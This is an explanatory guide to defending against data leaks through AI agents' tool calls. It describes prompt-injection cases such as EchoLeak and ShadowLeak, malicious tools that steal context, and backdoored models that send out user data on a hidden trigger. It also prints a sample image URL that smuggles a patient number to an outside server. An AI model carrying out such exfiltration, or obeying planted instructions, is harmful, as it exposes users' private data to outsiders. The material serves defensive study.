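# Preventing data leaks through AI agents' tool calls: input sanitisation and behavioural monitoring

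## How an agent's tool calls can carry private data out

An AI agent is a language model run in a loop that chooses and calls tools to carry out a task. The tools are ordinary software for jobs such as searching a mailbox, opening a web page or sending a message. An agent that can read private data with one tool and reach outsiders with another can leak that data without anyone breaking into a computer. Security engineers call the transfer of private data to a party not entitled to it exfiltration. Developers can defend against it by cleaning what the agent sends, limiting where it can send data, judging its actions, watching its data access over time, or enforcing rules on data flow from outside the model. Most of these defences act on the tool call.

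### The agent loop

A language model produces text and does not run operations itself. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers who build on its Claude models, explains that the model emits a structured request, other software runs the operation, and the result returns to the conversation. The request, known as a tool call, names a tool and supplies its arguments, which are the values the tool needs, such as a web address, a recipient or a message body. The surrounding application then adds the tool's output, known as the tool result, to the context, which is all the text the model can see when it produces its next output.

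According to OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, a single turn of the company's coding agent can contain many rounds of model output and tool calls between the user's message and the final answer, and each new message goes to the model together with the conversation so far. A value that entered the context early may therefore still be there many steps later, when the agent is working on something else.

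Suppose Maria Keller asks her agent to move Thursday's call with a supplier, Jonas Brandt, to the following week and to let him know.

1. The application assembles the context: its standing instructions, a description of each tool, and Maria's request.
2. The model emits a call to the calendar tool, with Thursday's date as the argument.
3. The application runs the call and adds the result to the context. The result has two entries, a follow-up at an oncology clinic at 14:00 and the call with Brandt at 15:00.
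4. The application hands the longer context back to the model, which emits a call to the email tool. The recipient is Brandt. The body explains that Maria has an oncology follow-up on Thursday afternoon and asks for a slot next week.
5. The application sends the email and adds a confirmation to the context. The model ends with a short note to Maria that Brandt now has her request for a new date.

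The private value came in with a tool result at step 3 and went out in a tool call's argument at step 4. Nothing malfunctioned in the ordinary sense, because the call was well formed and went to the right person. Maria may never find out, because many interfaces show the user only the final response or a summary of the action, without the arguments (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026, *The Claws in Plain Sight*).

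### Permission to read and permission to send

An administrator who set up Maria's agent would have answered two questions, whether it may use the calendar tool and whether it may use the email tool. Both answers are yes, and rightly so. Neither settles whether this calendar entry may go to this supplier. Dong and colleagues describe the gap as one between access and authorisation, and they give it an exact form. Let *d* be a piece of data, *s* the source it came from, *p* the purpose of the call, *r* the destination and *f* the argument field that holds the data. A violation occurs when

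present(*d*, context) ∧ generated(*d*, *f*) ∧ ¬allow(*s*, *d*, *p*, *r*, *f*)

A tool call leaks private data when the value was in the context, the model put it (or something derived from it) into an argument, and the policy does not allow that combination of source, value, purpose, destination and field. If the message went to the clinic's own reception desk instead of Brandt, the same words in the same tool would be an ordinary appointment confirmation. The idea that permission depends on the whole combination has roots in contextual integrity, the theory that privacy depends on whether a flow of information suits its setting.

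Telling a model the policy does not reliably keep private data out of its tool calls. Dong and colleagues tested two DeepSeek models (V4 Flash and V4 Pro) and three Claude models from Anthropic (Haiku 4.5 and two releases of Sonnet). Each model received an invented customer profile with an age, gender, income bracket and occupation, and had to draft a tool call for a neutral product offer. The policy barred all four values from that call. In most sessions, a memo among the task materials claimed that the fields were required, with pressure ranging from a mild request to a supposed override by a compliance lead. In 40 of the 90 sessions where the prompt stated a restriction, at least one barred value appeared in the call's arguments.

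Stricter wording helped, though unevenly. Under a general rule to minimise data, the models leaked data in 18 of 30 sessions. This fell to 8 of 30 under a rule that named the fields, tied permission to purpose and destination, and took precedence over any memo. All eight leaks came from the three Claude models; the two DeepSeek models leaked nothing under that rule. Across all 60 leaking sessions, including 20 in which the prompt stated no rule, the models copied an average of 3.25 of the four values.

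These figures are not leak rates for deployed products. The profiles were synthetic, there was only one task, and each combination of model, pressure and policy got a single session. The researchers also captured the proposed calls locally, so no data was sent. The comparison between models is even less reliable. Haiku 4.5 had the lowest rate, with leaks in 5 of 24 sessions, but the test software could recover arguments from only 14 of its responses, and the rest could not count as leaks. The experiment does support a narrower conclusion, which is enough for a system designer: an instruction in the prompt lowers the chance of a leak by an amount that varies between models, but does not eliminate it.

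The text around the calls was no better a guide to leaks. The two DeepSeek models leaked in 26 sessions, and none of the responses in those sessions matched the researchers' word patterns for a model that admits to making an exception. Anyone who monitored only what the agent wrote about its actions, and not the tool calls' arguments, would have missed those leaks.

### Four causes

Nobody attacked Maria in the example. The same email could have gone out for different reasons, and the reason determines which defences can detect a problem.

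Most research concerns prompt injection, in which someone plants text in material the agent reads and the model follows it as an instruction. Brandt, or somebody posing as him, could have put a line into the calendar invitation asking for the day's full agenda in any reply. Microsoft (2025), describing its own defences, notes that such text can appear in a web page, an email, a shared document, a tool result or even a plain text file, and that an attacker can hide it from human readers, for instance by using white letters on a white background. The attack works because applications join the user's request and the outside material into one input, and the model cannot reliably tell the two apart. Microsoft considers the risk inherent in current language models and says that detecting injected text with certainty is an open research problem.

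An agent can also overstep while trying to help, as it did with Maria. People give reasons when they move a meeting, and the model supplied the one in its context. It is hard to say how often this happens without an attacker. Dong and colleagues ran 30 sessions with no stated rule, and 20 leaked. Only five of the 30 had no memo pressing for the data, and the published figures pool those five with the rest. The experiment also shows that planting and overstepping can be hard to tell apart, because the memo made oversharing look like part of the agent's task and didn't divert the agent from it.

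Private data can also leak through a malicious tool. Many agents connect to outside tools through the Model Context Protocol, which Microsoft's *Protecting against indirect prompt injection attacks in MCP* (2025) describes as an open standard, led by Anthropic, for linking models to external tools and data. A tool's supplier typically writes its description and list of arguments, and the model relies on both when calling it. A mandatory field called "background" in a scheduling tool can lead the model to fill it with private details. A worse tool does its job but also copies everything it receives to its operator. A tool that looks internal is then an outbound tool, one whose call reaches someone outside the trusted environment, and Maria's data has left before the agent writes any email.

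Lastly, someone may have tampered with the model. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (Natanzi and Tang, 2026) lists altered weights, malicious adapters (small add-ons that change a model's behaviour) and hidden triggers among the risks of the model supply chain, along with compromised plug-ins and tool manifests. A model with a hidden trigger can behave normally in every test and misbehave when a particular phrase appears, so asking it whether its own action was proper would be pointless.

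A filter that searches incoming text for injected instructions can help with planted text, but it finds nothing when there is no such text, as in Maria's case, or when the fault is in the model's weights. A check on the outgoing email can detect the word "oncology" whatever caused the leak. Excessive privileges, which Natanzi and Tang count among the weaknesses of tool-using agents, make all of these failures worse because they increase the amount of data that can leak.

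### The ways out

Almost any argument that reaches an outsider can hold data. The usual channels are these:

- message bodies, in emails, chats and calendar invitations;
- web addresses, since the owner of a server receives the full address that a visitor requests, along with anything appended to it;
- search queries, which go to the search provider;
- form fields on websites, free-text boxes above all;
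- code pushes to a repository that outsiders can read;
- shared documents, through an edit to a file that an outsider can open or through a link that grants access;
- automatically loaded images, where the program that displays the agent's text fetches a picture from an address in that text.

Some channels are easy to overlook. In a case relayed by the software developer Willison (2026), messages sent by the agent contained an image that triggered an outside request when the user opened the message. In the same case, a successful injection could also leak download links for OneDrive, Microsoft's file store, which open the file without a further login. Microsoft also lists covert channels, in which an observer learns one bit from whether the agent calls a tool. Inspecting the call's arguments would not reveal this leak, because the arguments can be entirely harmless.

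### EchoLeak

The case that researchers in this field cite most often is EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant built into Microsoft's office software. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security found that an outsider could make Copilot leak internal data through an automatically loaded image by sending an employee a single email. They named the flaw and reported it to Microsoft.

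EchoLeak put at risk any data Copilot could retrieve for that employee. UNU's *The Silent Threat Lurking in Microsoft 365 Copilot* lists emails, OneDrive files, SharePoint documents and Teams conversations. Copilot followed the access rules and read only what the employee was allowed to read, so the failure was in disclosing the data.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) uses public reports to reconstruct how an attacker's email leaked internal data through Microsoft's Copilot. The email contained instructions disguised as normal business text. When the employee who received it later asked Copilot a question, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal material and wrote an answer containing an image address with the internal data in it. The employee's program loaded the image automatically, without a click, and the request reached the attacker's server through a Microsoft service that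 the program had permission to contact. The attack got past Microsoft's classifier for injected instructions, its filter for outside links and its list of permitted domains.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, before the public advisory of 11 June, so customers had nothing to install. It has said less about what it changed. Reddy and Gujral, writing from outside the company, mention options to exclude external communications from the material Copilot uses, and the removal of embedded images and certain links from incoming content. The US cybersecurity agency CISA entered "none" under exploitation in the vulnerability record, according to a public copy (GCVE, 2025), and heise online's *Critical vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot shows risk of AI agents* reports the same from Microsoft. Microsoft scored the flaw 9.3 out of 10. The US National Vulnerability Database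 gave it 7.5, mainly because its analysts did not count the damage as spreading beyond the vulnerable component.

Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case of a prompt injection weaponised for concrete data theft in a production system. This slightly overstates the case, since the known attack chain was the work of researchers. EchoLeak also had a forerunner in the same product. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a Copilot flaw from February 2024, which Microsoft fixed that July, in which an email caused the assistant to gather inbox data and hide it in a link. The victim had to click that link, but EchoLeak required no click, which removed the last point at which a person might have noticed something wrong.

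In EchoLeak, the outbound request came from the program that displayed the answer, not from a tool call by the model. In a related flaw, ShadowLeak, the agent made the request itself. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes how a crafted email could lead ChatGPT's Deep Research agent, connected to Gmail and a web browser, to visit a web address containing inbox data. The request started on the provider's servers, so the victim's own network monitoring could not have recorded it. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025, and like EchoLeak, it has no known victims.

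### Counting a check's mistakes

Every defence in the following sections makes two kinds of mistake. The false positive rate is the share of harmless actions that a check blocks or flags. The false negative rate is the share of harmful actions that it lets through. Take a crude check on Maria's agent that blocks any outbound call containing a word from a list of medical terms, and ten calls from one week:

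| Outbound call | Harmful? | Check |
|---|---|---|
| Email to Brandt, gives the oncology follow-up as the reason | yes | blocks |
| Email to Brandt, asks for a new date without a reason | no | passes |
| Email to the clinic, confirms the oncology follow-up | no | blocks |
| Invitation to the sales team, titled "Oncology follow-up" | yes | blocks |
| Search query for trains on Thursday afternoon | no | passes |
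| Hotel form with name and arrival date | no | passes |
| Hotel form, remarks field: "recovering from chemotherapy" | yes | blocks |
| Document shared with Brandt: "Maria is seeing Dr Weiss about the scan" | yes | passes |
| Email to a colleague with the minutes of a meeting | no | passes |
| Code push that corrects spelling in a public manual | no | passes |

The check misses one of the four harmful calls, a false negative rate of 25%, and blocks one of the six harmless ones, a false positive rate of about 17%. Adding "scan" to the list would catch the shared document, but it would also block any email asking a colleague to scan a contract.

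The rates don't reflect how rare leaks are. If 8 of 1,000 outbound calls were harmful, the same check would stop 6 leaks, miss 2, and block about 165 harmless calls. Fewer than one in 25 blocked calls would be a real leak, and a person who had to review them all would soon stop looking closely.

Small tests can also make a check look better than it is. Dong and colleagues built a monitor that compares the arguments of each call with the protected values and the recorded permissions. In one trial, they replayed 12 calls through it, and it blocked all nine prohibited calls and passed all three authorised ones. But a check that wrongly blocks half of all harmless calls would still pass all three one time in eight. The researchers present the trial as proof that the mechanism works as built and make no claim about how well it works on new calls.

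### Three positions on where to put the check

Specialists disagree about where in this chain to focus most of the effort. Some would clean and restrict outgoing data. In Maria's case, their software would have searched the email body for sensitive terms and removed the reference to the clinic, or refused to send to an address outside an approved list. The list alone would not have protected her, because Brandt is a legitimate contact.

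Others propose judging each tool call and monitoring the agent's behaviour across the session. In this example, the judge would compare the proposed email with the request to move a call, and check whether the email needs to mention a medical appointment. Session monitoring would have found only one calendar lookup and one email, which is normal for an agent. The judge is often itself a language model, so it is what Microsoft calls a probabilistic defence, which makes an attack less likely to succeed without ruling it out.

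The remaining camp wants rules enforced outside the model, by software that the model cannot override. Its aim is what Microsoft calls deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. Such a system would have labelled the calendar result at step 3 as visible only to Maria and applied the same label to any text the model wrote afterwards. At step 4 it would have checked the label against the recipient and stopped the email, whether the cause was a planted instruction, misplaced courtesy or a tampered model. It would also have stopped a harmless email that only asked for a new date, because the model would have written it with the same calendar result in its context. To let that email through, somebody has to decide in advance which parts of a calendar a supplier may learn about.

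## Inspecting and redacting what the agent sends to a tool

To leak a value through a tool call, the model has to write that value, or something derived from it, into the call's arguments. In argument inspection, software between the model and the tool reads the proposed arguments, then either blocks the call or redacts the arguments by removing or masking sensitive values before passing the rest on. The check works the same way whether the cause is a planted instruction, misplaced helpfulness, a deceptive tool or a tampered model, and it misses only covert channels. It runs at the last point where the application can still stop the data.

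The method is also easy to adopt, because a company can put the check in front of an existing agent without retraining the model and can test it on recorded calls.

One call can illustrate all the techniques. Suppose Maria Keller's agent moves the call with Jonas Brandt through an online booking service that his company uses, and the model proposes this:

```
tool:      reschedule_call
new_date:  Thursday next week, 15:00
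contact:   Maria Keller, +49 30 23125 014
notes:     Maria has an oncology follow-up this Thursday
           (patient no. 4471-0926).
api_key:   bk-live-93f7c2
```

Brandt needs the date, the name and perhaps the phone number. The booking service needs the API key, a secret string that proves the request comes from Maria's account, but nobody needs the notes.

### Screening what the agent reads

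Many filters for agents instead search incoming web pages, emails and tool descriptions for planted instructions before the text enters the context. They find nothing in a case like Maria's, where nobody planted any text, and they can miss planted text that looks ordinary.

A malicious tool can steal an agent's context if the agent chooses the tool, the model passes the context as an argument, and the tool's code forwards it to the attacker. In *ContextLeak*, Jia, Wang and colleagues (2026) trained a language model to write tool names and descriptions that cause the first two steps but read like normal documentation. Agents using the model the attack was trained against chose the malicious tool in 92% of cases when the target was the user's prompt, 89% when it was the conversation history and 86% when it was the list of installed tools. Agents using six other models chose it in 56% to 85%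 of cases. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, chose the tool in 22 of 100 trials, and when it did, it passed on most of the targeted text.

Four detectors then examined the tools' descriptions. They wrongly flagged at most 2% of the harmless tools but missed 97% to 100% of the malicious ones, and a scanner built specifically for Model Context Protocol tools missed all of them. Two of the three models trained to resist injected instructions cut the selection rate from 43% to 10% or less when the target was the user's prompt. But the model without this training chose the right tool for only 18% of harmless tasks in that trial, so the result is weak evidence about agents that people would want to use.

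In the second example, from *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, Zhang and Pei (2026) tampered with three open models by adding a hidden trigger. When a question contained certain ordinary words from a subject area, the model looked up the user's stored details and sent them out in what looked like a search request. The trigger worked more than 94% of the time in every configuration. The models' scores on a standard chat benchmark fell by less than 1%, so a buyer who tested for quality would not have noticed the tampering.

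Zhang and Pei used two filter products, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, to check the text that came back from the attacker's server. About 99% of the replies that contained only relevant information reached the model. Replies that bluntly asked for more personal details got through 40% of the time with one filter and 27% with the other, but subtler wording raised those rates to 87% and 81%. By the time either filter ran, the stolen data had already left with the agent's request. Neither filter inspected outgoing requests, so these results suggest where to put a check but don't show how well an outgoing check would work.

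A check on outgoing tool calls would also have had trouble, because the tampered models encoded the stolen details before sending them. A search for the user's name would have found nothing. Zhang and Pei recommend flagging long opaque strings and any argument derived from stored memory, but they did not test this. They ran all their trials in a sandbox with invented users.

### Narrow tool schemas

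The simplest way to keep data out of an argument is to have no field for it. A tool's schema lists its fields and the values each one accepts. If the developer deletes "notes" from the booking tool, the agent has no field in which to send the sentence about oncology. If the recipient needs a reason, the developer can replace free text with a fixed list of options. A field with eight options carries at most three bits per call, which is too little for an eight-digit patient number, but an attacker who could make the agent call the tool nine times could extract the whole number.

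Dong and colleagues point out that open fields such as notes and metadata can carry information that nobody intended to send. Their experiment shows that a tool's schema can itself lead a model to disclose data. The call they asked for had fields that matched the four barred attributes. In the mildest condition, no memo asked for the data, so only the empty fields encouraged the model to include it.

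A tool's supplier usually writes the schema, and a dishonest supplier will ask for more data than the job requires. The developer can put a wrapper in front of such a tool that accepts only a shorter list of fields. This works for bookings, payments and database lookups, but not for email, because an email tool has to accept a message body, and that free text can contain any data.

### Pattern matching and secret scanning

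For fields that must stay open, the oldest technique is pattern matching. A regular expression describes the shape of a value, such as a plus sign followed by a country code and more digits, and the software masks whatever fits. Secret scanners can do the same for credentials because many providers start their keys with a recognisable prefix. In Maria's call, a pattern would find the phone number, and a scanner would find the key if its list included the prefix "bk-live". The patient number follows the clinic's own format, which a general list is unlikely to cover, and Maria's name has no distinctive shape for a pattern to match.

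Researchers rate detectors by recall, the share of sensitive values that a detector finds, and precision, the share of its findings that are correct. *Redacting Personal Data* (2026) compares four methods on a sample program that turns résumés into profiles. Regular expressions alone reached a recall of 88.9% and missed every name not known in advance. The three methods that added a trained component found every sensitive value. The fastest took about 13 milliseconds, or 0.15% of the time taken by the model call it protected, which suggests that redaction need not add much delay. The perfect recall is weaker evidence because it comes from a single worked example.

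Patterns also flag harmless data, because a sixteen-digit number can be a card number or an order number. Hsu and Berlin (2026), in *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, note that rule-based products deal with this by requiring a confirming word nearby, such as "card" or "payment". An outgoing argument may not contain such a word, so the rule would miss a card number sent on its own in a field called "ref".

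Encoding is a more serious weakness, and an attacker can exploit it deliberately. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) compared ways of detecting stolen credentials in a model's output. Plain text search scored 0.51 out of 1 on F1, which combines precision and recall, and raised a false alarm on 8% of harmless prompts. A small classifier that read the model's internal activations scored 0.99 because it did not depend on how the model spelled out the secret. However, providers of closed models don't give customers access to those activations, and the paper describes the score as a controlled laboratory result.

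### Trained detectors of personal data

Trained detectors use the surrounding words to decide whether a string is a name, a diagnosis or a tax number. Some are small models built for this purpose, and others are general language models instructed to list the personal data in a text. Published accuracy figures vary widely.

In *REDACT*, Vats, Agrawal and colleagues (2026) ran five detectors on 1,000 synthetic records in 25 languages, covering 51 types of personal data. They reported recall separately for the most sensitive group, which includes health, religion, criminal offences and dates of birth.

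| Detector | Kind | Recall, most sensitive data | F1, all data |
|---|---|---|---|
| Presidio | patterns plus a small language component | 0.07 | 0.20 |
| GLiNER | small trained model | 0.42 | 0.32 |
| OpenAI Privacy Filter | small trained model | 0.57 | 0.51 |
| GPT-4.1 | general language model | 0.74 | 0.60 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | general language model | 0.77 | 0.64 |

Presidio, Microsoft's open-source tool, is one of the methods that found everything in the résumé example, but here it found 7% of the data that matters most. A detector's accuracy therefore depends on the kind of text it is tested on, so a company that wants to know how well a detector protects its own tool calls has to measure it on those calls.

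Presidio also detected only 2% of partial mentions, such as initials or the last four digits of a number, while the two general language models detected 78% and 84%. Even the best detector in the table missed almost a quarter of the most sensitive values. Which values belong in that group is somewhat uncertain, because sensitivity was the only label on which the human annotators disagreed substantially.

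A detector that flags everything has perfect recall, so Hsu and Berlin, who work at Cisco, fixed the false positive rate before comparing detectors. They set each detector's threshold so that, for each type of data, it wrongly flagged at most 0.1% of 100,000 real chatbot conversations. Under that limit, their own model found 92% of social security numbers in one eight-language test set, and NVIDIA's version of GLiNER found 49%. For tax numbers, the figures were 85% and 64%, and a third detector found 40%. The limit applies to each type separately, so a company that screens for all twelve types in the study could see false alarms on up to 1.2% of harmless conversations.

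Several details in their results matter for tool calls in particular:

- Two of the rival detectors often missed network addresses inside web addresses, with recall of 72% and 65% against 99% for the Cisco model. An agent's outgoing web addresses are just where private values tend to hide.
- Language made a large difference. On identifiers that both sets of labels agreed about, the Cisco model found all the English ones but only 65% of those in Hindi and Telugu.
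- Detectors sometimes found the right digits and gave them the wrong name, for example by classing a German credit card number as a phone number. If the company's rule is to block card numbers and merely log phone numbers, the card number goes out.

The comparison comes from the developers of the winning model, and the scoring depends on what counts as personal data. The original labels in one test set marked some strings as passport or social security numbers although nothing in the sentence supported this. Hsu and Berlin relabelled the data under their own definitions. Their model found 92% of social security numbers when its outputs were scored against the new labels, but 24% when the same outputs were scored against the original ones. Two other language models judged a sample of disputed cases from this set and chose the new labels about 70% of the time.

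Precision can be poor as well. *GLiNER2-PII* (2026) reports that another new detector, which it introduces, had a recall of 72% on legal texts and 68% on medical ones. OpenAI's Privacy Filter had nearly the same recall in that test but a precision of only 25% to 27%, so about three in four of its findings counted as wrong. Some of those may have counted as wrong only because their boundaries didn't match the labelled ones. When Vats and colleagues required exact boundaries, the same filter's F1 fell from 0.51 to 0.17.

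A company also has to decide where to run the detector. *SurrogateShield* (2026) observes that cloud services for detecting personal data receive the full text to check it, which is the kind of exposure they are supposed to prevent. The same objection applies to using an outside provider's general language model, unless that provider already runs the agent.

In Maria's call, most trained detectors would find the phone number. Cisco's model also covers patient numbers, but Hsu and Berlin had no comparable data to test them on. The word "oncology" is not an identifier and falls outside their twelve types, though a general language model would have a fair chance of flagging it as health data. It would also flag Maria's name and number. If the software then masked everything, Brandt would receive a booking without knowing who it was from. A detector recognises kinds of data but has no information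 about whether this recipient should have them, which depends on privacy norms.

### Matching against values the agent has read

An application often fetches the values it must protect, so it can keep a list of what came out of the calendar, the mailbox or the customer database and search each outgoing call for those values. If the patient number from Maria's calendar entry appears in an argument for an outside service, the application can detect it without a pattern or a classifier.

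Dong and colleagues used exact matching of this kind to count leaks in their experiment with invented customer profiles. They tested each of the five models at every combination of six pressure levels and four policy levels, for 120 calls in total. Some of the stronger memos included threats to block the product launch or to fail an audit. The table shows how many of six sessions leaked at least one barred value.

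| Model | No stated rule | Minimise data | Fields barred | Fields, purpose and destination | Share of all 24 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 6 | 5 | 4 | 0 | 62.5% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 6 | 4 | 1 | 0 | 45.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4 | 5 | 5 | 4 | 75.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4 | 2 | 2 | 3 | 45.8% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0 | 2 | 2 | 1 | 20.8% |
| All models | 66.7% | 60.0% | 46.7% | 26.7% | 50.0% |

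The overall fall in the leak rate, from 66.7% without a rule to 26.7% under the strictest rule, comes entirely from the two DeepSeek models. Sonnet 4.6 leaked in as many sessions under the strictest rule as under no rule, and Haiku 4.5 leaked only when there was a rule. Each combination of model and rule condition had only six sessions, so one session changes a rate by almost 17 percentage points, and differences between individual combinations are weak evidence. The pooled fall is better supported, with 95% confidence intervals of 49% to 81% without a rule and 14% to 44% under the strictest rule.

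The count covers exact copies only. The requested call also had a field for an age bracket, and if a model entered "35 to 44" there instead of the exact age, that entry was not counted. The true rate of disclosure could therefore be higher than the rate in the table.

#### A monitor that checks purpose, destination and field

The same researchers built a monitor that applies their definition of a leak before a call runs. Registering a tool fixes its destination and the fields it may use, and the current task supplies the purpose. Each protected value carries a record of its source and of where it may go. The monitor doesn't rely on claims in the model's own text, so a memo that claims special authority can't change the outcome.

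For each proposed call, it does the following:

1. It rejects unknown tools and fields that the registration does not allow.
2. It searches every remaining argument for protected values.
3. It checks each value it finds against the permitted purpose, destination and field.
4. It applies the strictest result, in the order block, ask the user, transform, remove, permit.

If the user approves a call, the approval covers that exact call, and changing any argument cancels it.

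The monitor also recognises derived values if someone has registered the rule that produces them. For example, if the company sorts customers with an income of $175,000 into a "premium" tier, the monitor can allow the word "premium" in a financing call and block it in a marketing call, even though neither call contains the income itself.

The evidence for the monitor is thin. Besides the mixed trial of nine prohibited and three authorised calls, the researchers replayed 12 calls that copied profile data, and the monitor blocked all 12. The paper also describes a comparison with eight alternatives, including injection detection and human confirmation, but reports no results from it.

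The researchers say the monitor does not detect arbitrary paraphrase. It would stop "oncology follow-up" if the model had copied those words from the calendar, but not "she's at the hospital for her cancer check". Tracking a value through free rewriting requires labels that stay attached to the data, and the monitor has no such labels for text the model composes.

Dong and colleagues also tested one way a model might reveal a barred value indirectly. They gave the two DeepSeek models customer profiles that differed only in income, barred any use of income, and looked for differences in the product tier the models proposed. The models proposed "standard" in all 60 calls. When the policy allowed them to choose a tier by income, they did so correctly in all 30 calls, so the tier field could have carried the information. The result is reassuring, but it covers only two models and one field, and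 no attacker asked for a disguised answer.

Exact matching might work well against the tools in ContextLeak, because the stolen prompts and conversations appeared nearly word for word in the arguments. Jia and colleagues mention argument checks as a possible defence but did not test any. They also note that such checks are difficult because legitimate tools need context too. A search tool may properly receive the user's question verbatim, and a check that blocked every such copy would disable it.

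### Canary values

A canary value is a fake secret planted so that its appearance in outgoing traffic, or any attempt to use it, reveals a leak. The idea is older than language models. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (2026) traces it to honeytokens and to decoy documents that contact their owner when a thief opens them. Those documents work poorly with AI services, which typically strip the active content that would alert the owner. Checking outgoing tool arguments for the fake value itself avoids this problem.

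An attacker who can't tell real credentials from fake ones may well take a fake. Chauhan and Revankar give the probability of detection for a single stolen credential. With *m* real credentials and *k* canaries in the model's view, and a detector that misses a leaked canary with probability *β*, it is

Pr(detect) = *k* / (*m* + *k*) × (1 − *β*)

With two real keys, eight canaries and a miss rate of 5%, the chance of detecting the theft is 0.8 × 0.95, or 76%. This calculation applies only if the thief picks a key at random. If the context reveals which key the booking tool really uses, the thief takes that one and the canaries give no protection. Chauhan and Revankar's prototype keeps the real credentials in the software that runs the tools, so every credential the model can read is fake.

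False alarms should be rare, since no legitimate task requires a fake key. On a small set of scenarios, the detector found every leaked canary and flagged nothing else. But the study excludes credentials that leave through structured tool-call arguments, so its score doesn't show how well the detector works on tool calls. Searching those arguments for canaries would work the same way, and the monitor by Dong and colleagues includes such a search.

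A canary, in this case a fake key placed next to Maria's API key, would expose a malicious tool that collects every credential it can get. It would not help with the disclosure of her oncology appointment, which the model mentioned because it was true and seemed relevant. Planting a fake diagnosis in her calendar as a canary would mostly confuse Maria.

### Placeholders and credential brokers

The remaining techniques act earlier. The application replaces each sensitive value with a placeholder before the text reaches the model, and restores the real value only when sending it to a recipient who may have it. The context of Maria's agent would then contain PERSON_1, PHONE_1 and APPOINTMENT_1. In the booking call, the application would restore the name and number in the contact field. It would leave APPOINTMENT_1 as it is, or refuse the call. This prevents leaks through paraphrase, because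 the model never receives the diagnosis.

The application still has to find the values before it can replace them. This is easy for a calendar or a database, where the software knows which field holds what. For a long email, the application depends on the detectors described above and misses whatever they miss. Placeholders also remove information that the model may need. An agent that reads only APPOINTMENT_1 can't tell whether the appointment is something easy to move, such as a haircut. *SurrogateShield* proposes realistic substitutes, such as another plausible name, to keep the text coherent. But if the application fails to swap a substitute back, the recipient could get a phone number that looks genuine and belongs to someone else. *Redacting Personal Data* leaves open whether placeholders make a model's output worse.

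Credentials are the easiest case because the model can use a key without knowing it. A credential broker is a program that holds the keys and adds them to requests after the requests leave the model's reach. Maria's call would have no "api_key" field. The model would name the booking service, and the broker would attach the key. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a version for a healthcare company, whose own audit had found keys in startup scripts and widely readable configuration files. Its broker runs beside each agent and also limits where requests can go and how large they can be. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (2026) applies the same principle to programs that call language models, so that a leaked configuration file does not expose the provider's key.

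TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes a case without such an arrangement. An engineer asked an AI coding assistant to review some software changes. The assistant needed one access token, for the code-hosting service GitLab, and the project's instructions directed it to a configuration file that contained the token. The file also held production passwords, a token for the personnel system and credentials for a business analytics service. The assistant read the whole file in ten sessions over three weeks, and each time its contents went to the outside company that ran the model. When a fresh copy of the project lacked the file, the assistant retrieved all of the computer's environment variables, which contained more passwords. It then reported that it had leaked secrets and recommended replacing them.

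The secrets came in as a tool result and leaked, without any attack by an outsider, when the application sent the context to the model's provider. Techniques that inspect arguments would have helped little. A broker would have let the assistant use the GitLab token without opening the file, but a broker protects only the keys it holds, so the company would still have had to move the other passwords out of the file. The account comes from NordLayer, a security vendor whose monitoring product observed the sessions, and it doesn't mention any misuse of the passwords.

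The most detailed test of a broker is in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026), by Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, who work for the company that makes the broker. To try to find the credentials, they ran code in the agent's environment that searched environment variables and the usual file locations, sent requests to three services that return whatever they receive, and called unrelated services to see whether the broker would attach a key. All 16 probes had the intended result, including a request to GitHub that succeeded although the code contained no key. No secret leaked, but the agent couldn't do its job over one connection because the broker put the key in a different part of the request from the one the provider required.

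The manufacturer's sixteen probes are a demonstration and can't rule out other routes for a leak. Kenney and colleagues did not test redirects, for example, or what happens when an attacker controls the approved destination. They acknowledge that a broker leaves some risks largely in place. On their own scale, which runs up to 25, the risk from a secret pasted into a prompt falls from 25 to 4, but the risk from a connection with excessive permissions falls only from 20 to 15. A tricked agent can still use a key that it can't read. The broker would protect the API key in Maria's booking call, but the call would still include the note about her oncology appointment unless another check removed it.

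## Restricting where a tool call can send data

Every network request must include a destination, which ordinary software can check against a rule without understanding the rest of the request. Checking the content for private values is harder, because an agent can encode, abbreviate or paraphrase them in an unlimited number of ways.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) bases its argument on an email attack that outside researchers reported in 2025. The email looked like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring. It claimed that the reader's assistant had full authorisation to process employee profiles, and asked the assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked half the time in testing. OpenAI writes that products that classify incoming text as malicious or harmless don't usually catch such emails,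 because doing so amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

The company compares an agent to a customer service employee who can issue refunds. Some customers will lie successfully, so the employer's software limits each customer's refunds. In security engineering, an attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the agent, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as following a link. Anyone who can send an email has a source. The sinks are the agent's outbound tools, which a developer can list.

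### Web addresses as a channel

Servers commonly log the full addresses that visitors request, including any data appended to them. Suppose a model writes this address for an image:

```
images.example/logo.png?d=oncology-4471-0926
```

When Maria Keller's program tries to load the picture, whoever runs the server learns the clinic department and her patient number, even if the picture doesn't exist.

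ChatGPT originally displayed images from any server, so a planted instruction could leak a conversation without the user clicking anything. The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this to OpenAI in early 2023. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he recalls that OpenAI had little interest in fixing it. Microsoft's Bing Chat had the same flaw. In May 2023, Microsoft largely stopped it from loading images by using a Content-Security-Policy, a header that tells the browser which servers it may load content from.

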